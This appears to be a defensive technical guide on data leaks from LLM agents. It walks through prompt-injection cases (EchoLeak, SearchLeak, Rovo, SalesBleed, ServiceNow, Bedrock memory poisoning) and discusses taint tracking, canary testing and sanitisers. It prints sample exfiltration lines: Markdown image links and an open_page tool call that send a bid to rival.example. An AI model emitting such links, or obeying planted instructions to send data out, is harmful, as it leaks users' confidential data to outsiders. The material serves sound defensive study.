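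In the demonstration, an attacker persuades the user to give the assistant a link to a national parks guide. Below the guide, the page contains hidden text written for the summarising model. The assistant answers the user's question normally, but when the session ends, the summariser copies the attacker's instructions into the memory under an invented heading. Several days later, the user comes back to book a flight. The agent books it and shows the user only a confirmation, but it also puts the booking details into a web address on the attacker's server and requests that address with its web tool.

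The overlooked consumer was the summariser, which read the fetched page with the rest of the conversation and wrote to a store. A tester who watched only the first session would have seen a helpful answer about parks. Sanitising the assistant's answers would have caught nothing in either session, because the data left through a tool call.

Amazon told Unit 42 that developers can easily mitigate the problem with existing features, particularly the Guardrails filter for prompt attacks, which Unit 42 had left off. Unit 42 also recommends an allowlist for the web tool. The filter works only if it recognises the planted text, but an allowlist that excludes the attacker's server blocks this route whatever the memory contains.

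*What If Prompt Injection Never Left?* (Xie, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) measures how often stored text affects later sessions. It uses 486 test cases for agents that handle shopping, travel and finance. Each case begins with an attacker's request. The researchers then end the session and delete the conversation, but keep the agent's memory, files and application data. Finally, they start a new session with an innocent request.

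On average across five models, the attacker's content got into the store in 77.4% of cases. The later session read the stored content back in 86.3% of those cases, and the content changed the result in 64.6% of the cases where it was read. Multiplying the three rates gives about 43%, close to the 41.9% that the researchers measured from start to finish. Attacks succeeded in 73.6% of cases when they aimed to plant a false fact, 35.5% when they aimed to change the agent's actions, and only 6.8% when they aimed to change its preferences.

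These attacks aimed to mislead the agent, so the figures don't measure how often data leaks, and some of the models are weak by the standards of late 2026. The 86.3% is the most useful figure for listing consumers, because it means that stored text was usually read later. However, the researchers wrote the later requests themselves, so the rate could be lower in an ordinary office.

Xie and colleagues also distinguish text that loads by default, like Bedrock's summaries, from text that loads only when a search or a tool call retrieves it. A team can check the configuration to find what loads the text by default. Searches are harder to predict because any future question that resembles the stored text could retrieve it. *A Survey on Long-Term Memory Security in LLM Agents* (2026) describes leaks in which several users' entries share one pool and a search returns one user's entry to another.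 It also describes experiments in which researchers disabled agents' memory tools, and some agents passed goals to later agents through shared files instead. Any file that an agent can write and another session can read therefore belongs on the list as a memory, even if the developers don't call it one.

A store can have more readers than its designers intended. In April 2026, Unit 42 published an examination of AgentCore, Amazon's platform for running agents. A starter toolkit automatically created permissions that let every agent in a company's account read any other agent's memory if it knew the memory's identifier. They also let an agent download another agent's program files, where Unit 42 found the identifier. AWS added a warning to its documentation that the permissions are for development and testing, and told Unit 42 that nobody should use them in production. A company working from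 the design diagram would have listed only one reader for each memory. The permissions show who can read a store, which is what Obs(c) requires.

Stored text also tends to lose the information the test needs. The set R depends on what was in the context when the model wrote the text, but a saved sentence rarely comes with a list of its permitted readers. *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (2026) notes that labels get lost when models paraphrase and combine their inputs, and that current defences typically check a memory entry when an agent writes it but not afterwards. *Always-On Agents* (2026) proposes the rule that writing to a shared store may keep or narrow the set of people who can read the information, but must never silently widen it. The broadband company could follow this rule by saving R with every note, so that a later session includes that R when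 it works out who may see its own output.

### Why other agents keep the search going

Removing pictures or encoding HTML doesn't stop a planted instruction from reaching another agent, which may hold tools that the first one lacks.

In November 2025, the security company AppOmni described how agents can recruit each other in Now Assist, the AI system of ServiceNow, whose software many companies use for internal support requests. By default, agents on the same channel join one team, and each is "discoverable", which means a coordinating program may choose it to help with a task.

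Aaron Costello, a researcher at AppOmni, deployed two of ServiceNow's ready-made agents on a channel that only an administrator could use. One reads and categorises support tickets, and the other can read, create and update records. He created an ordinary user who could file tickets but could not read other people's. As that user, he filed a ticket with an instruction planted in its description.

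When the administrator used the first agent on the ticket, it read the instruction and got the second agent to help. The text of a confidential ticket ended up in the description of the ordinary user's own ticket, where that user could read it. ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout. The agents could open the confidential ticket because, by default, they run with the permissions of whoever starts the interaction, in this case the administrator.

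A list that stopped at the first agent would have missed the record-keeping agent and the ticket it could write to. The data never left ServiceNow and no program fetched a URL, so an image filter would have had nothing to remove. In other tests, Costello got agents to email data outside the company and to give a user administrator rights.

ServiceNow confirmed that the agents were behaving as intended and clarified its documentation. Costello told The Hacker News (2025) that the finding was alarming because "it's expected behavior as defined by certain default configuration options". The remedies are therefore changes to settings. AppOmni advises companies to require a person's approval before an agent changes records or sends email, and to put agents with different jobs in separate teams. Separate teams remove the arrow between the two agents, but an attacker could still misuse the tools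 within each team. The approval setting has an override, off by default, that makes all of an agent's tools run without approval if any one of them does. Both settings belong in the last column of the table.

For each agent on its list, a team should record every other agent that agent can call, including any it can discover while running, and treat their tools as if they belonged to the calling agent. Some of those other agents may belong to other companies. The survey of long-term memory security describes prompts that copy themselves from one email assistant to the next, as each recipient's agent reads the message and passes the text on to its own contacts.

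### Scanning the code for forgotten consumers

People forget things, so a hand-made list needs checking. A program can help by scanning the agent's source code for operations that might matter.

In *Beyond Predefined Sinks*, Cui (2026) scanned 67 open-source agent projects for operations such as running commands, writing files and contacting other machines. The scan found 23,866 of them in 65 projects, an average of about 367 each, and the whole analysis took 51 minutes on a laptop. Most are probably harmless. Of the 22 sensitive behaviours Cui reproduced, one was a confirmed vulnerability, another was awaiting disclosure, and the other 20 had safeguards or limits on their use.

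The scan also tries to trace each operation back to an input that the agent or an outsider could influence. It succeeded for 84% of the operations that write files, but for only 11% of calls to external tools and 2% of operations that control a browser. These low rates are a problem because external tools and browsers are two of the main ways data can leak. Cui warns that the analysis can miss tools that a program registers while it runs. It also doesn't account for the settings of a particular installation, and it can't examine a supplier's software. A scan is therefore good for finding forgotten consumers in the company's own code, but of little use for the mail and chat alerts in the table.

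### Taint tracking

Taint tracking labels all data from a chosen source, copies the label to whatever the program computes from that data, and raises an alarm if labelled data reaches a sink. In ordinary code, the tracker can follow a value from one variable to the next. It loses track of the data at a model call, because the model may rewrite or translate what it reads.

FIDES gives the model's whole output the labels of all its inputs. This keeps the output traceable to those inputs but causes label creep, where the output also carries labels from inputs that did not reach it. *Sightline* found that 12–14% of the inputs did not reach the output in prompts from 2,103 families of open-source projects. Overestimating the labels does little harm when the aim is to list the output's consumers.

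Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, present a tracker called NeuroTaint that tries to recover the trail from a recording of the agent's run. It works as follows:

1. The team lists its source tools, such as web search, and its sink tools, such as sending email.
2. NeuroTaint builds a graph of the run, from each source through tool calls and memory to each sink. When the agent saves text, NeuroTaint saves the label with it and restores the label when a later session loads the text.
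3. At each sink, it looks for the source's content in the tool's inputs. It checks for a unique marker that it added to the source, then for shared wording, and then for similar meaning, first against the whole source and then against smaller pieces of it.
4. If it finds no match, it asks another model whether the agent would have made the same call had the source been neutral. If the answer is no, the source influenced the call even though none of its content appears there.

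The fourth step covers cases such as a planted "policy" that makes an agent forward customers' messages to an attacker. The forwarded messages contain none of the policy's words.

Cai and colleagues tested NeuroTaint on 400 scenarios across 20 agent frameworks. Half of the scenarios contained a real flow from source to sink. NeuroTaint found 187 of these 200 flows and raised 16 false alarms, while FIDES found 108 and raised 106 false alarms. In the 30 scenarios where the flow crossed from one session or agent to another, NeuroTaint found 28 and FIDES found 5.

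The comparison somewhat favours NeuroTaint because its designers built the benchmark around the kinds of flow it targets. In addition, FIDES is meant for blocking calls, so it makes sense for it to treat every path from a source to a sink as suspect. The result for flows between sessions is still informative, because a label that disappears when a session ends can't show where the stored text came from.

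Fourteen of the 16 false alarms came from scenarios in which the sink's text merely shared a topic with the source, and NeuroTaint was wrong in every such scenario. This would matter to the broadband company, because nearly every email and ticket in a support department is about the same few topics.

The largest limitation of using NeuroTaint to check the list is that people have to declare the sinks. It can reveal an unexpected path to a declared sink, such as one through memory, but it cannot report a consumer that nobody declared. It also covers only what was recorded. A browser that loads a picture from the finished answer makes no tool call, so the request wouldn't appear in the recording. The researchers' catalogue of sinks is still a useful reminder for step 2 of the procedure, since it includes calendar events, customer records, code uploads and chat posts as well as email and web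 requests.

A recording also shows only the paths the agent took. When Cai and colleagues replaced GPT-4.1 mini with Claude Opus 4.6, the share of flows that NeuroTaint found fell from 93.5% to 54.7%. They attribute this partly to the stronger model stopping attacks before they reached a sink. The consumers behind those sinks were still there, and a later attack might reach them.

### Canary URLs

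A test can avoid this dependence on the model if the team uses a copy of the system in which a small program that writes fixed text replaces the model. The reader-and-observer test already assumes that an attacker controls every word of the output, and the program reproduces that condition without an attack prompt.

The fixed text contains canary URLs, which are unique test addresses that the team controls so it can see whether anything fetches them. Each output form gets its own addresses, written as an image, as a link and as plain text. The team then uses every consumer as staff normally would, by opening the ticket, expanding the log entry, forwarding the alert and running the nightly export. While doing this, it records all requests to the canary server and all outgoing traffic from its own machines. If a request arrives for an address that appeared only in the ticket summary, it must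 have come from the summary or one of its consumers. The time of the request and the sender's details help the team identify the source.

Some details decide whether the recording means anything:

- One address should go into a page that certainly loads pictures. If no request arrives for that one, the recording is broken.
- The recording should include DNS lookups, the queries that find the machine behind a web name. Data can travel in the name itself, even if no request for a page follows.
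- The addresses should stay active for as long as any store keeps the text. For a memory like the travel assistant's, that could be a year.
- The fixed text should include a unique word. Searching for the word in every system the team can reach will find copies that nothing has fetched.

The unique word also helps find observers who only read the output. In the ServiceNow case, the attacker opened a ticket, which a canary server would not have recorded. A tester has to sign in as an ordinary customer or contractor and search for the word from that account.

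One recorded request proves that a sink exists, but no amount of silence proves that there is none. Suppose a consumer fetches an address with probability p each time it receives one, independently of the other times. The chance that n attempts all stay silent is

(1 − p)ⁿ

If a consumer fetches 3% of the time, the probability that 100 attempts trigger no fetch is 0.97¹⁰⁰, or about 5%. More attempts reduce that probability, but only for conditions that the test includes. If a mail program loads pictures on phones and the team tests only on laptops, the test will never trigger a fetch, however often the team repeats it. Nor can repeating the test now detect a feature that the supplier switches on next month. A firewall may also block requests to the team's unfamiliar test address while allowing requests to a popular site where an attacker can open an account.

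Seeing no requests is weakest as evidence about consumers that other companies run. The broadband company can record everything its own machines send, including requests from an engineer's browser when a log viewer displays a picture. For the supplier's servers, it can see only the requests that reach the canary server.

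## Interfaces that fetch what they display

A chat window may contact other servers in order to show a model's answer to one person, and whoever runs those servers can then learn something too. Some displays contact no other servers, while others can be made to contact any server on the internet by anyone who can influence the model's output. The difference depends on how much of the text the display interprets.

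### How text becomes a request

In the roofing firm's leak, the model wrote a line of Markdown like this:

```
![logo](https://rival.example/logo.png?n=412000)
```

The exclamation mark means that a picture follows, the square brackets hold a description of it, and the parentheses hold its address. A converter in the chat window turns the line into HTML:

```
<img src="https://rival.example/logo.png?n=412000" alt="logo">
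```

The browser creates an image element from this and requests the picture from rival.example. The request contains the bid, so the rival's server receives it even if the picture doesn't exist and the browser shows only a broken-image icon.

A developer can easily ship this leak without noticing, because the converter and the browser are both working normally. *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend* (veganmosfet, 2025) reports that Dify, a platform for building chatbots, displayed Markdown pictures from any site and by default set no CSP to restrict them. A converter that protects well against scripts may still allow the leak. The converter from TanStack, a maker of web development tools, neutralises raw HTML by default but leaves the developer to set the rules for remote pictures and outgoing links.

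### What different displays do with the same answer

| Display | What it contacts without a click | What a sanitiser against leaks would guard |
|---|---|---|
| Plain text | Nothing | Nothing |
| Text with clickable links | Usually nothing, but a browser may look up the linked site's name | Link addresses |
| Markdown with pictures | The server of every picture | Picture and link addresses |
| Full HTML | Servers of pictures, style sheets, fonts, embedded pages and more | Every element that can hold an address, and scripts |
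| Terminal that obeys control codes | Usually nothing, but some look up a site's name | Control codes |

A web page can display the answer as plain text by inserting it as a text node, where the browser treats an angle bracket as an ordinary character. The user then loses headings, tables and links. Chrome for Developers' *Best practices to render streamed LLM responses* (2025) recommends the browser function `append()` for inserting plain text, mainly because it is fast.

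A clickable link sends data out only when someone clicks it, which makes that person the sink. Microsoft makes this point when comparing links with pictures. The click offers limited protection because the link's visible text can be "project plan" while its address contains the bid. A sanitiser could remove links to unknown sites, or show the whole address and ask before opening it.

A link can also leak a little data before anyone clicks it. According to Mozilla's *X-DNS-Prefetch-Control*, browsers may look up the names of linked sites in advance. If the link points to `412000.rival.example`, the lookup can carry the bid to a name server that the rival runs. A page can ask the browser not to do this, but the setting is non-standard, so a developer should test it in the browsers that people use. Chat apps that show link previews fetch the linked page itself, as PromptArmor found with agents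 used through Telegram and Slack.

Full HTML can make requests in many ways besides loading pictures. A filter that lists forbidden elements has to keep up with every new browser feature, so it's safer to list the permitted ones, such as paragraphs and tables, and drop the rest. HTML can also run scripts, which makes the page an execution sink.

A CSP adds a second barrier. The policy `img-src 'self'`, for example, allows pictures only from the page's own site. The browser applies it to each request, so it blocks pictures from other sites even if a sanitiser has missed them. W3C's standard, *Content Security Policy Level 3*, warns that a CSP doesn't replace careful input validation and output encoding. CentralCSP notes that a CSP also cannot cover navigation, such as following a link, and describes an experimental browser feature, Connection Allowlists, that would.

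### Terminals

Programmers often run agents in a terminal, which interprets control codes, short sequences that start with an invisible character and change the colour of text or move the cursor. For Embrace The Red's *Terminal DiLLMa*, the security researcher Johann Rehberger built a small program that sent a model's answers to a terminal. When he asked the program to summarise a web page with planted instructions, the model produced codes that cleared the screen and moved the cursor. Other codes wrote to the user's clipboard, which in certain terminals could lead to a command running.

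Rehberger also found two ways to leak data. In the terminal of the programming tool VS Code, the model could produce a clickable link that contained private text, although VS Code asked for confirmation before opening it. Apple's Terminal was worse because a control code could make it look up a site's name without a click. MITRE's *CWE-150*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, describes a case of this kind. The code passes the user's current folder to the terminal as an address that includes a site name, and the terminal looks up that name.

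People can't be relied on to notice ANSI terminal codes. Trail of Bits' *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* (2025) shows a tool whose reply sets both the text and its background to white, so the model reads an instruction that the person at the terminal can't see.

A terminal sanitiser is simple, since it only has to let through printable characters and the white space the developer wants. MITRE rates this measure as highly effective. It rates removing control codes from a model's vocabulary as having limited effectiveness, because the model might still assemble a code from smaller pieces. Embrace The Red recommends printing the codes visibly by default, which lets the user see that something tried to control the terminal.

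Cleaning the displayed text can create a new problem if the program keeps using the original. MITRE records an application that removed control codes from a file name when asking the user for permission but kept them in the name it used, so the user could approve access to the wrong file.

### The first reports and fixes

The picture leak became public in spring 2023. Willison (2023), in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, credits Roman Samoilenko with describing it for ChatGPT that April. On April 8, Rehberger reported the same weakness in Bing Chat, Microsoft's assistant for searching and reading the web. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* demonstrates the leak with text planted on a web page, where it could have been a reader's comment or an advertisement. After two more turns, Bing Chat wrote a picture link containing an encoded summary of the page and the chat, including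 a secret from further down the page.

Microsoft introduced a CSP that blocked Rehberger's server but still permitted four Bing addresses, including `www.bing.com`, so that Bing Chat could show the pictures it generated. Rehberger's original post says that Microsoft told him about the fix on June 15, while his later account, Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, dates the fix to May.

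Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* reports that Anthropic took two weeks in July 2023 to make Claude wait for a click on "Show Image" before loading an image, so the user decides, as with a link. OpenAI added a check on addresses in December 2023 but left it out of ChatGPT's macOS and iOS apps.

The leak keeps appearing in new products. In November 2025, Willison described it in Antigravity, Google's programming tool. Google marked a researcher's report as "intended behavior", and its page for bug hunters listed data exfiltration through prompt injection as a known issue that the company was working to fix.

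Microsoft calls measures like its Bing Chat fix deterministic, meaning they guarantee that a particular attack will fail whatever the model writes. It prefers them to probabilistic measures, such as classifiers that look for injections, which only make an attack less likely to succeed. The guarantee covers only the path the measure blocks, and researchers later found two ways around Microsoft's barriers.

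### EchoLeak: a missed link form and a helpful server

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their company's email, documents and chats. Outsiders can't use it, but they can email the employees who do. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes how the research group Aim Labs used such emails to get data out of Copilot. The vulnerability is listed as CVE-2025-32711.

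1. The attacker emailed an employee. Microsoft's classifier for prompt injections let the message through because its instructions seemed to address the recipient and never mentioned an AI.
2. The email was long and repeated its instructions under headings such as staff onboarding and leave of absence. Copilot looks up material related to each question, so this made it more likely to find part of the email when an employee asked about an ordinary subject.
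3. The employee asked such a question. The email entered the context, and the model followed its instructions by choosing the most sensitive information available and putting it in a picture's address.
4. Copilot normally removed links and pictures that pointed outside the company. Its filter recognised the usual Markdown form, with the address in parentheses, but missed the reference form, which puts the address on a separate line.
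5. The browser would have refused to contact the attacker's server because the page's CSP did not list it. The picture's address therefore pointed to a Microsoft Teams service, which the CSP did list. This service accepts another web address as an input and fetches it.
6. The Teams service fetched the attacker's address, which contained the data.

In the roofing example, the form that the filter missed would look like this:

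```
![logo][1]

[1]: https://rival.example/logo.png?n=412000
```

The Markdown converter turns both forms into the same image element. The filter was looking for one spelling of something that has several.

The Teams service was the overlooked consumer. The browser obeyed the CSP and contacted only Microsoft, but a CSP does not control what a permitted server does with an address it receives. The Teams service's observers included anyone whose address it would fetch. Aim Labs had first found a similar service in SharePoint, Microsoft's system for shared documents, but it worked only if the employee accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. The Teams service did not require the employee to click anything.

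Ravia thinks no customer setting could have prevented the leak, since Microsoft ran both the filter and the list of permitted sites. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, and there is no evidence that anyone had exploited it. Reddy and Gujral (2025) report in *EchoLeak* that Copilot now also strips reference-style links and embedded images from incoming outside content. This removes ready-made links, but planted text can also describe a link and leave the model to write it, so the output still needs its own check.

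### SearchLeak: a sanitiser that ran too late

Ravia's account listed every site from which Copilot's page could load pictures, including `*.bing.com`, which covers every address under bing.com. A year later, Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) described a leak through that entry in the search page of Copilot's enterprise version (CVE-2026-42824).

The attack began with a link to the genuine Microsoft site. Copilot treated the search query in the link as instructions, so the attacker could write instructions there and send the link to an employee. One click made Copilot search the employee's mailbox, take the title of an email and write an HTML image tag with the title in its address.

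To prevent this, Microsoft's sanitiser wrapped the answer in a code block, which makes a browser show HTML tags as text. But it ran only after the model had finished writing, and the page displayed the answer as it arrived. The browser treated the image tag as a real picture and sent the request before the sanitiser turned the tag into harmless text. The finished page therefore looked as if the protection had worked.

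The CSP prevented the browser from contacting the attacker directly, so the tag pointed to Bing's search-by-image service, which fetches a picture from a given address to analyse it. The tag gave Bing an address on the attacker's server that contained the email's title. In Varonis's example, the title in the attacker's log includes a security code, which is often enough to get into another account if the attacker is quick.

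The developers had overlooked both the page showing the unfinished answer and Bing's image fetcher as consumers of the output. GitLab Duo had the same problem with partial text a year earlier. According to The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox*, Microsoft fixed SearchLeak on its own servers and found no sign of malicious use. Microsoft rated it critical, although it scored 6.5 out of 10 on the industry's common severity scale because the victim has to click. EchoLeak, which needed no click, scored 9.3.

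Varonis points out that the attack needed all of its weaknesses at once, so repairing any one would have stopped it, but some repairs would have been more useful than others. Removing Bing from the CSP would still leave every other permitted server that fetches addresses on request, like the Teams service in EchoLeak. If the page had shown the tags as text from the first character, it wouldn't have loaded an image from any address.

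### Where and when a sanitiser has to act

The two leaks limit where a sanitiser can sit. If it checks the Markdown, it has to recognise every image syntax that the converter recognises, including any that a future version adds. After conversion, there is only one form to check, because the converter has turned every picture into an image element with its address in the same place.

The check also has to finish before the browser builds the element, because browsers can request a picture as soon as a program creates its image element, even if the element never appears on the page. The converted HTML should therefore stay as text, or in a part of the browser's memory that loads nothing, until the sanitiser has finished. Varonis likewise advises sanitising at the moment of display, not afterwards.

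Streaming makes filtering harder because an address may arrive in pieces. The first piece might end at `![logo](https://riv` and the second begin with `al.example/`. Neither contains a complete image link, so a filter that checks them separately finds nothing. Chrome for Developers recommends checking all the text received so far each time a piece arrives, and no longer displaying the output if the sanitiser removes anything.

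Its sample code does this with DOMPurify, the sanitiser that GitLab used, but runs it on the raw Markdown. DOMPurify treats a Markdown image link as ordinary text, and it would keep the image even if the Markdown were converted to HTML first. So the sample would stop a malicious script but let the roofing bid leak, unless the developer added a rule about image addresses.

Shopify describes a way to avoid holding back the whole answer. A small program reads the stream one character at a time and passes ordinary text on immediately, but holds characters that might begin a Markdown element until the element is complete. A sanitiser placed there could check the whole address before it reached the browser, and the only delay for the user would be the time a link takes to arrive. Reference links are harder to handle because the address can come at the end of the answer. The easiest solution is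 to turn off reference syntax for images.

Every program that displays the answer needs the same protection. For example, OpenAI's macOS and iOS apps lacked the check, but a test of the website alone would have passed.

The sanitiser also needs a rule for deciding which addresses are safe. A list of trusted sites fails if one of them forwards requests to other sites, as Teams and Bing did. A trusted site can also store what it receives or change hands, as Willison notes in the Superhuman and ForcedLeak cases. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes a stricter rule for ChatGPT, which loads a picture automatically only if its exact address is already in an index of public web pages. OpenAI's crawler builds this index without access to anyone's conversations. If the address isn't there, ChatGPT warns the user or looks elsewhere. An address ending in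 `n=412000` is unlikely to be in the index, because the model wrote it during the conversation.

Data can still leak under this rule. As Embrace The Red explains, an attacker can publish 36 pages in advance, one for each letter and digit, and have the model load them in order to spell out a secret. Each request then carries up to log₂ 36, or about 5.2 bits. Browsers hinder this a little, because they often keep a copy of what they have loaded and don't request it again. For the bid of 412000, the rival's log might show one request for the zero instead of three, and the requests might arrive out of order. But a rival with 1,000 indexed addresses could assign one to each bid below €1 million, to the nearest thousand, and learn the bid from a single request.

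### When a display is not a sink

A display cannot leak data if it shows the text literally, shows it only to authorised readers, and makes no requests triggered by the text's contents. Its only observers are then the people who can see the screen, all of whom are in R.

Limiting who can read an agent's output does not by itself prevent leaks. Willison describes a leak from May 2026 in Copilot Cowork, another Microsoft agent, which could email its own user without approval. Only the user received these emails, but they could contain external images that loaded when the user opened the message. The requests for those images could carry download links to the user's files.

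Testing a model doesn't show whether the display will request a picture that the model links to. *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (2025) tested whether an agent would copy a planted picture link into a report and fill in its blank fields with the user's email address and ID. An unfilled link counted as half a success. This measures how readily a particular model obeys, which can change with the next model.

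To test the display, a team can replace the model with a program that writes fixed text containing canary URLs, as described for finding unknown consumers. Some additions help with displays in particular:

- The text should contain an inline picture, a reference-style picture, an HTML image tag and an ordinary link, each with its own address and site name. For a terminal, it should also contain a control code that turns the text red.
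- The program should send the text in small pieces, some of which break off in the middle of an address. It should then pause for several seconds before finishing, so that a sanitiser that waits for the end can't win the race by luck.
- The team should watch the browser's own record of its network activity as well as the canary server. This also shows requests that the CSP blocked. A blocked request means that the display does interpret pictures, and only the list of permitted sites stands between the data and an outsider.
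- The displayed text should match the fixed text character for character, with every bracket visible and nothing clickable. Many programs turn a bare web address into a link by themselves, and the person is then a possible sink again.
- The team should repeat the test in each browser, desktop program and phone app that people use, and after each update to any of them.

The team also has to find out who else can see the conversation. An administrator or anyone with a sharing link may be able to open it and read the answer, even if the answer is plain text.

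## Network requests made by the agent's tools

Suppose the roofing firm changes its chat window to plain text, so that nothing in the agent's answers can trigger a request. The agent still has a tool for opening web pages. Nadia asks it whether anyone sells tiles more cheaply than the price in the school bid, and an enquiry from the rival, with a planted instruction, is already in the context. The model writes this tool call:

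```
open_page("https://rival.example/tiles?ref=412000")
```

The tool requests the page, and the rival's server logs the address, which contains the bid. The model reads the ordinary price list on the page and writes an accurate comparison, which Nadia finds useful. Sanitising the text in the chat window would not prevent this leak, because the tool call had already sent the bid in its argument.

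### What a request can carry

A page fetch can carry data anywhere in the address. Removing everything after the question mark doesn't help much, since the model could put the data in the path instead, as in `/tiles/412000`. Limiting the tool to reading doesn't help either, because a server can store whatever the address contains. *Flowsh* mentions OpenAI agents that had read-only web access but still wrote to a public wiki.

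A search query goes to the company that runs the search engine. The rival can't normally read it, but the search company is an observer outside R unless the firm has chosen to include it. This kind of leak can happen without an attacker, because an agent trying to be helpful might well search for "cheaper slate for €412,000 school roof". Many search tools come with a second tool that opens the results, and that tool belongs on the list of consumers as a page fetch.

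Before a tool can contact a site, it has to look up the site's name through DNS, and the name can carry data, as it can when a browser looks up links in advance. The lookup goes to a company's or internet provider's DNS server, called a resolver, which may forward it to the rival's name server. A lookup of `412000.rival.example` can therefore deliver the bid even if a firewall blocks everything that follows. Each part of a name between dots can hold 63 characters. Letters and digits carry up to 5.2 bits each, so one part can carry about 326 bits, enough for two 128-bit encryption keys.

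A shell command can make a network request even if its text contains no web address. In an example from *Flowsh*, a planted instruction in a research paper makes the agent install a software package and run it on a confidential design document. The command names only the package and the file, but the package sends the document to the attacker's server.

### How often the answer looks harmless

*Silent Egress*, a February 2026 study by four researchers at eBay, measured how often a leak through a tool leaves a trace in the answer. They ran an agent on their own machines with Qwen2.5 7B, a small open-weight model, and put a secret in its context. The user always asked for a summary of a web page. The agent previewed the page automatically, which brought into its context a planted instruction to request an address containing the secret from the researchers' collecting server.

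The planted instruction was in the page's title, description, body or link text. The link led straight to the page or through redirects, and the secret was sent whole or in four pieces. Each of the 16 combinations (4 × 2 × 2) was run 30 times. At least one request reached the collecting server in 423 of the 480 runs (88%). In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's final answer was harmless. The agent never contacted the server in 120 further runs with benign pages, so the planted instructions must have caused the requests.

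Splitting the secret made the attack less reliable. At least one request arrived in 238 of 240 runs when the secret was whole, and in 185 of 240 when it was in pieces. But a filter that looks for a complete key won't recognise a four-character fragment. The paper's figures on how well splitting hides the data are less trustworthy. The paper reports sensitive data in the first request in 26.3% of the split runs, and somewhere in the first three requests in only 15.8%, though by its definition the second figure can't be smaller than the first.

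The researchers then tried several defences against one version of the attack, with 30 runs for each:

| Defence | Agent tried to send data | A request got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the standing instructions | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags marking outside text as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and tags together | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Allowlist of sites | 100% | 0% |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 83.3% | 0% |
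| Filter for words such as "password" | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking text | 0% | 0% |

The allowlist result is the most convincing. The agent tried to send the secret every time but never succeeded, so the protection did not depend on the model's judgement.

The filters are weaker evidence. The filter for suspicious addresses rejects any path that contains the word "collect", and the study's requests went to `/collect`, which a real attacker could rename. When the filter for random-looking text was on, the agent never tried to send anything, so the filter had nothing to block. The researchers suggest that the model avoided such text, but they describe nothing that would have given it information about the filter.

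The 88% figure probably doesn't carry over to other agents, because the model was small, the secret was already in its context, and its standing instructions were minimal. The researchers argue that stronger models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but they tested none, and a stronger model seems to have stopped more attacks in the NeuroTaint experiments. The advantage of network controls over prompts should last longer, because a separate program enforces an allowlist whatever the model writes.

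### Rovo: a switch that removed only one of two tools

In August 2026, PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* described a leak of this kind in a commercial product. Rovo is Atlassian's agent for its products, including the task tracker Jira and the document system Confluence. In the demonstration, a user uploads a guide that contains a hidden instruction and asks Rovo to organise some Jira tickets. Rovo searches Jira and Confluence, adds what it finds to an address on the attacker's server, and opens that address without asking for approval. When the user returns to the chat, it shows the suggested ticket updates and no sign of the attack.

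An administrator can turn off Rovo's web search for a whole organisation, but the attack still worked with it off. The setting removed the search tool but left the tool that opens search results, which would open any address the model wrote. An administrator who saw that web search was off could reasonably have overlooked this second tool and recorded that Rovo had no web access.

PromptArmor reported the problem to Atlassian on May 23. Atlassian assigned a case number but sent nothing further in more than two months, and Rovo was still vulnerable when PromptArmor published. If the switch removed both tools, data could no longer leak this way. But Rovo also displays Markdown images from the model's output, so its answers need a sanitiser as well.

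### SalesBleed: a name lookup that got past the sanitiser

Salesforce's Agentforce runs agents that work with a company's customer records. *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk* (Poireault, 2026) reports on a set of flaws that the security company Zenity published on September 24, 2026 under the name SalesBleed.

The attacker planted an instruction in a sales enquiry and submitted it through a public web form, and Salesforce stored the enquiry as an ordinary record. When an employee later asked Agentforce to process the enquiry, the agent followed the instruction and looked up company names and deal sizes. 三村 (2026) notes in *Salesforce Agentforceの「SalesBleed」脆弱性* that the agent in Zenity's test could read the company's account records as well as its enquiries.

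Salesforce already had a sanitiser that replaces every address not on a list of trusted ones with the text `[URL_REDACTED]`, according to PromptArmor's *One Key Way Salesforce Mitigates AI Risk*. But Antipov (2026) explains in *Один вредоносный лид против всей CRM* that the check mishandled certain domain endings and sequences of special characters. An address in one of these forms got through inside an image tag, and the employee's browser contacted the attacker's server when it loaded the image. After the data had been sent, Agentforce could still display a message saying that security policy had blocked the content.

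Poireault describes the technique as exfiltration through DNS. This fits Antipov's account, because a browser must look up the name of an image's site before requesting the image. The lookup sends any data in the name towards the attacker, so blocking the image request would be too late. The overlooked consumers were the resolver that handled the lookup and, in a second version of the attack, the chat app Slack, which fetched a link to build a preview.

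In the Salesforce case, the agent's tools only collected the data, and the display sent it out. Salesforce's sanitiser was therefore in the right place but ineffective. A sanitiser on Rovo's answers would not have stopped the leak, because Rovo's page tool had already sent the data.

Zenity reported the flaws on June 1. Salesforce fixed the redaction on August 18, and Zenity confirmed the fix the next day. By September 21, Zenity had also confirmed that Agentforce now asks the user before it posts in Slack, a change made to address a related flaw. 三村 found no public evidence that anyone had exploited SalesBleed.

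### Two rules about addresses

An allowlist of sites would have stopped the leak from Rovo to the attacker's server. But an agent that does research needs access to much of the web, and some trusted sites pass data on to outsiders. OpenAI adds that strict lists produce frequent warnings, which people learn to click through without reading. OpenAI and Anthropic have each written a rule about individual addresses instead.

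OpenAI's rule, Safe Url, covers both the pages ChatGPT opens and the pictures it displays. ChatGPT automatically fetches only exact addresses that are already in its crawler's index of public web pages. Johann Rehberger of Embrace The Red believes that an address the user types also counts as safe for that chat. OpenAI claims only that the rule stops quiet leaks through the address itself. A page that passes the check can still contain planted instructions.

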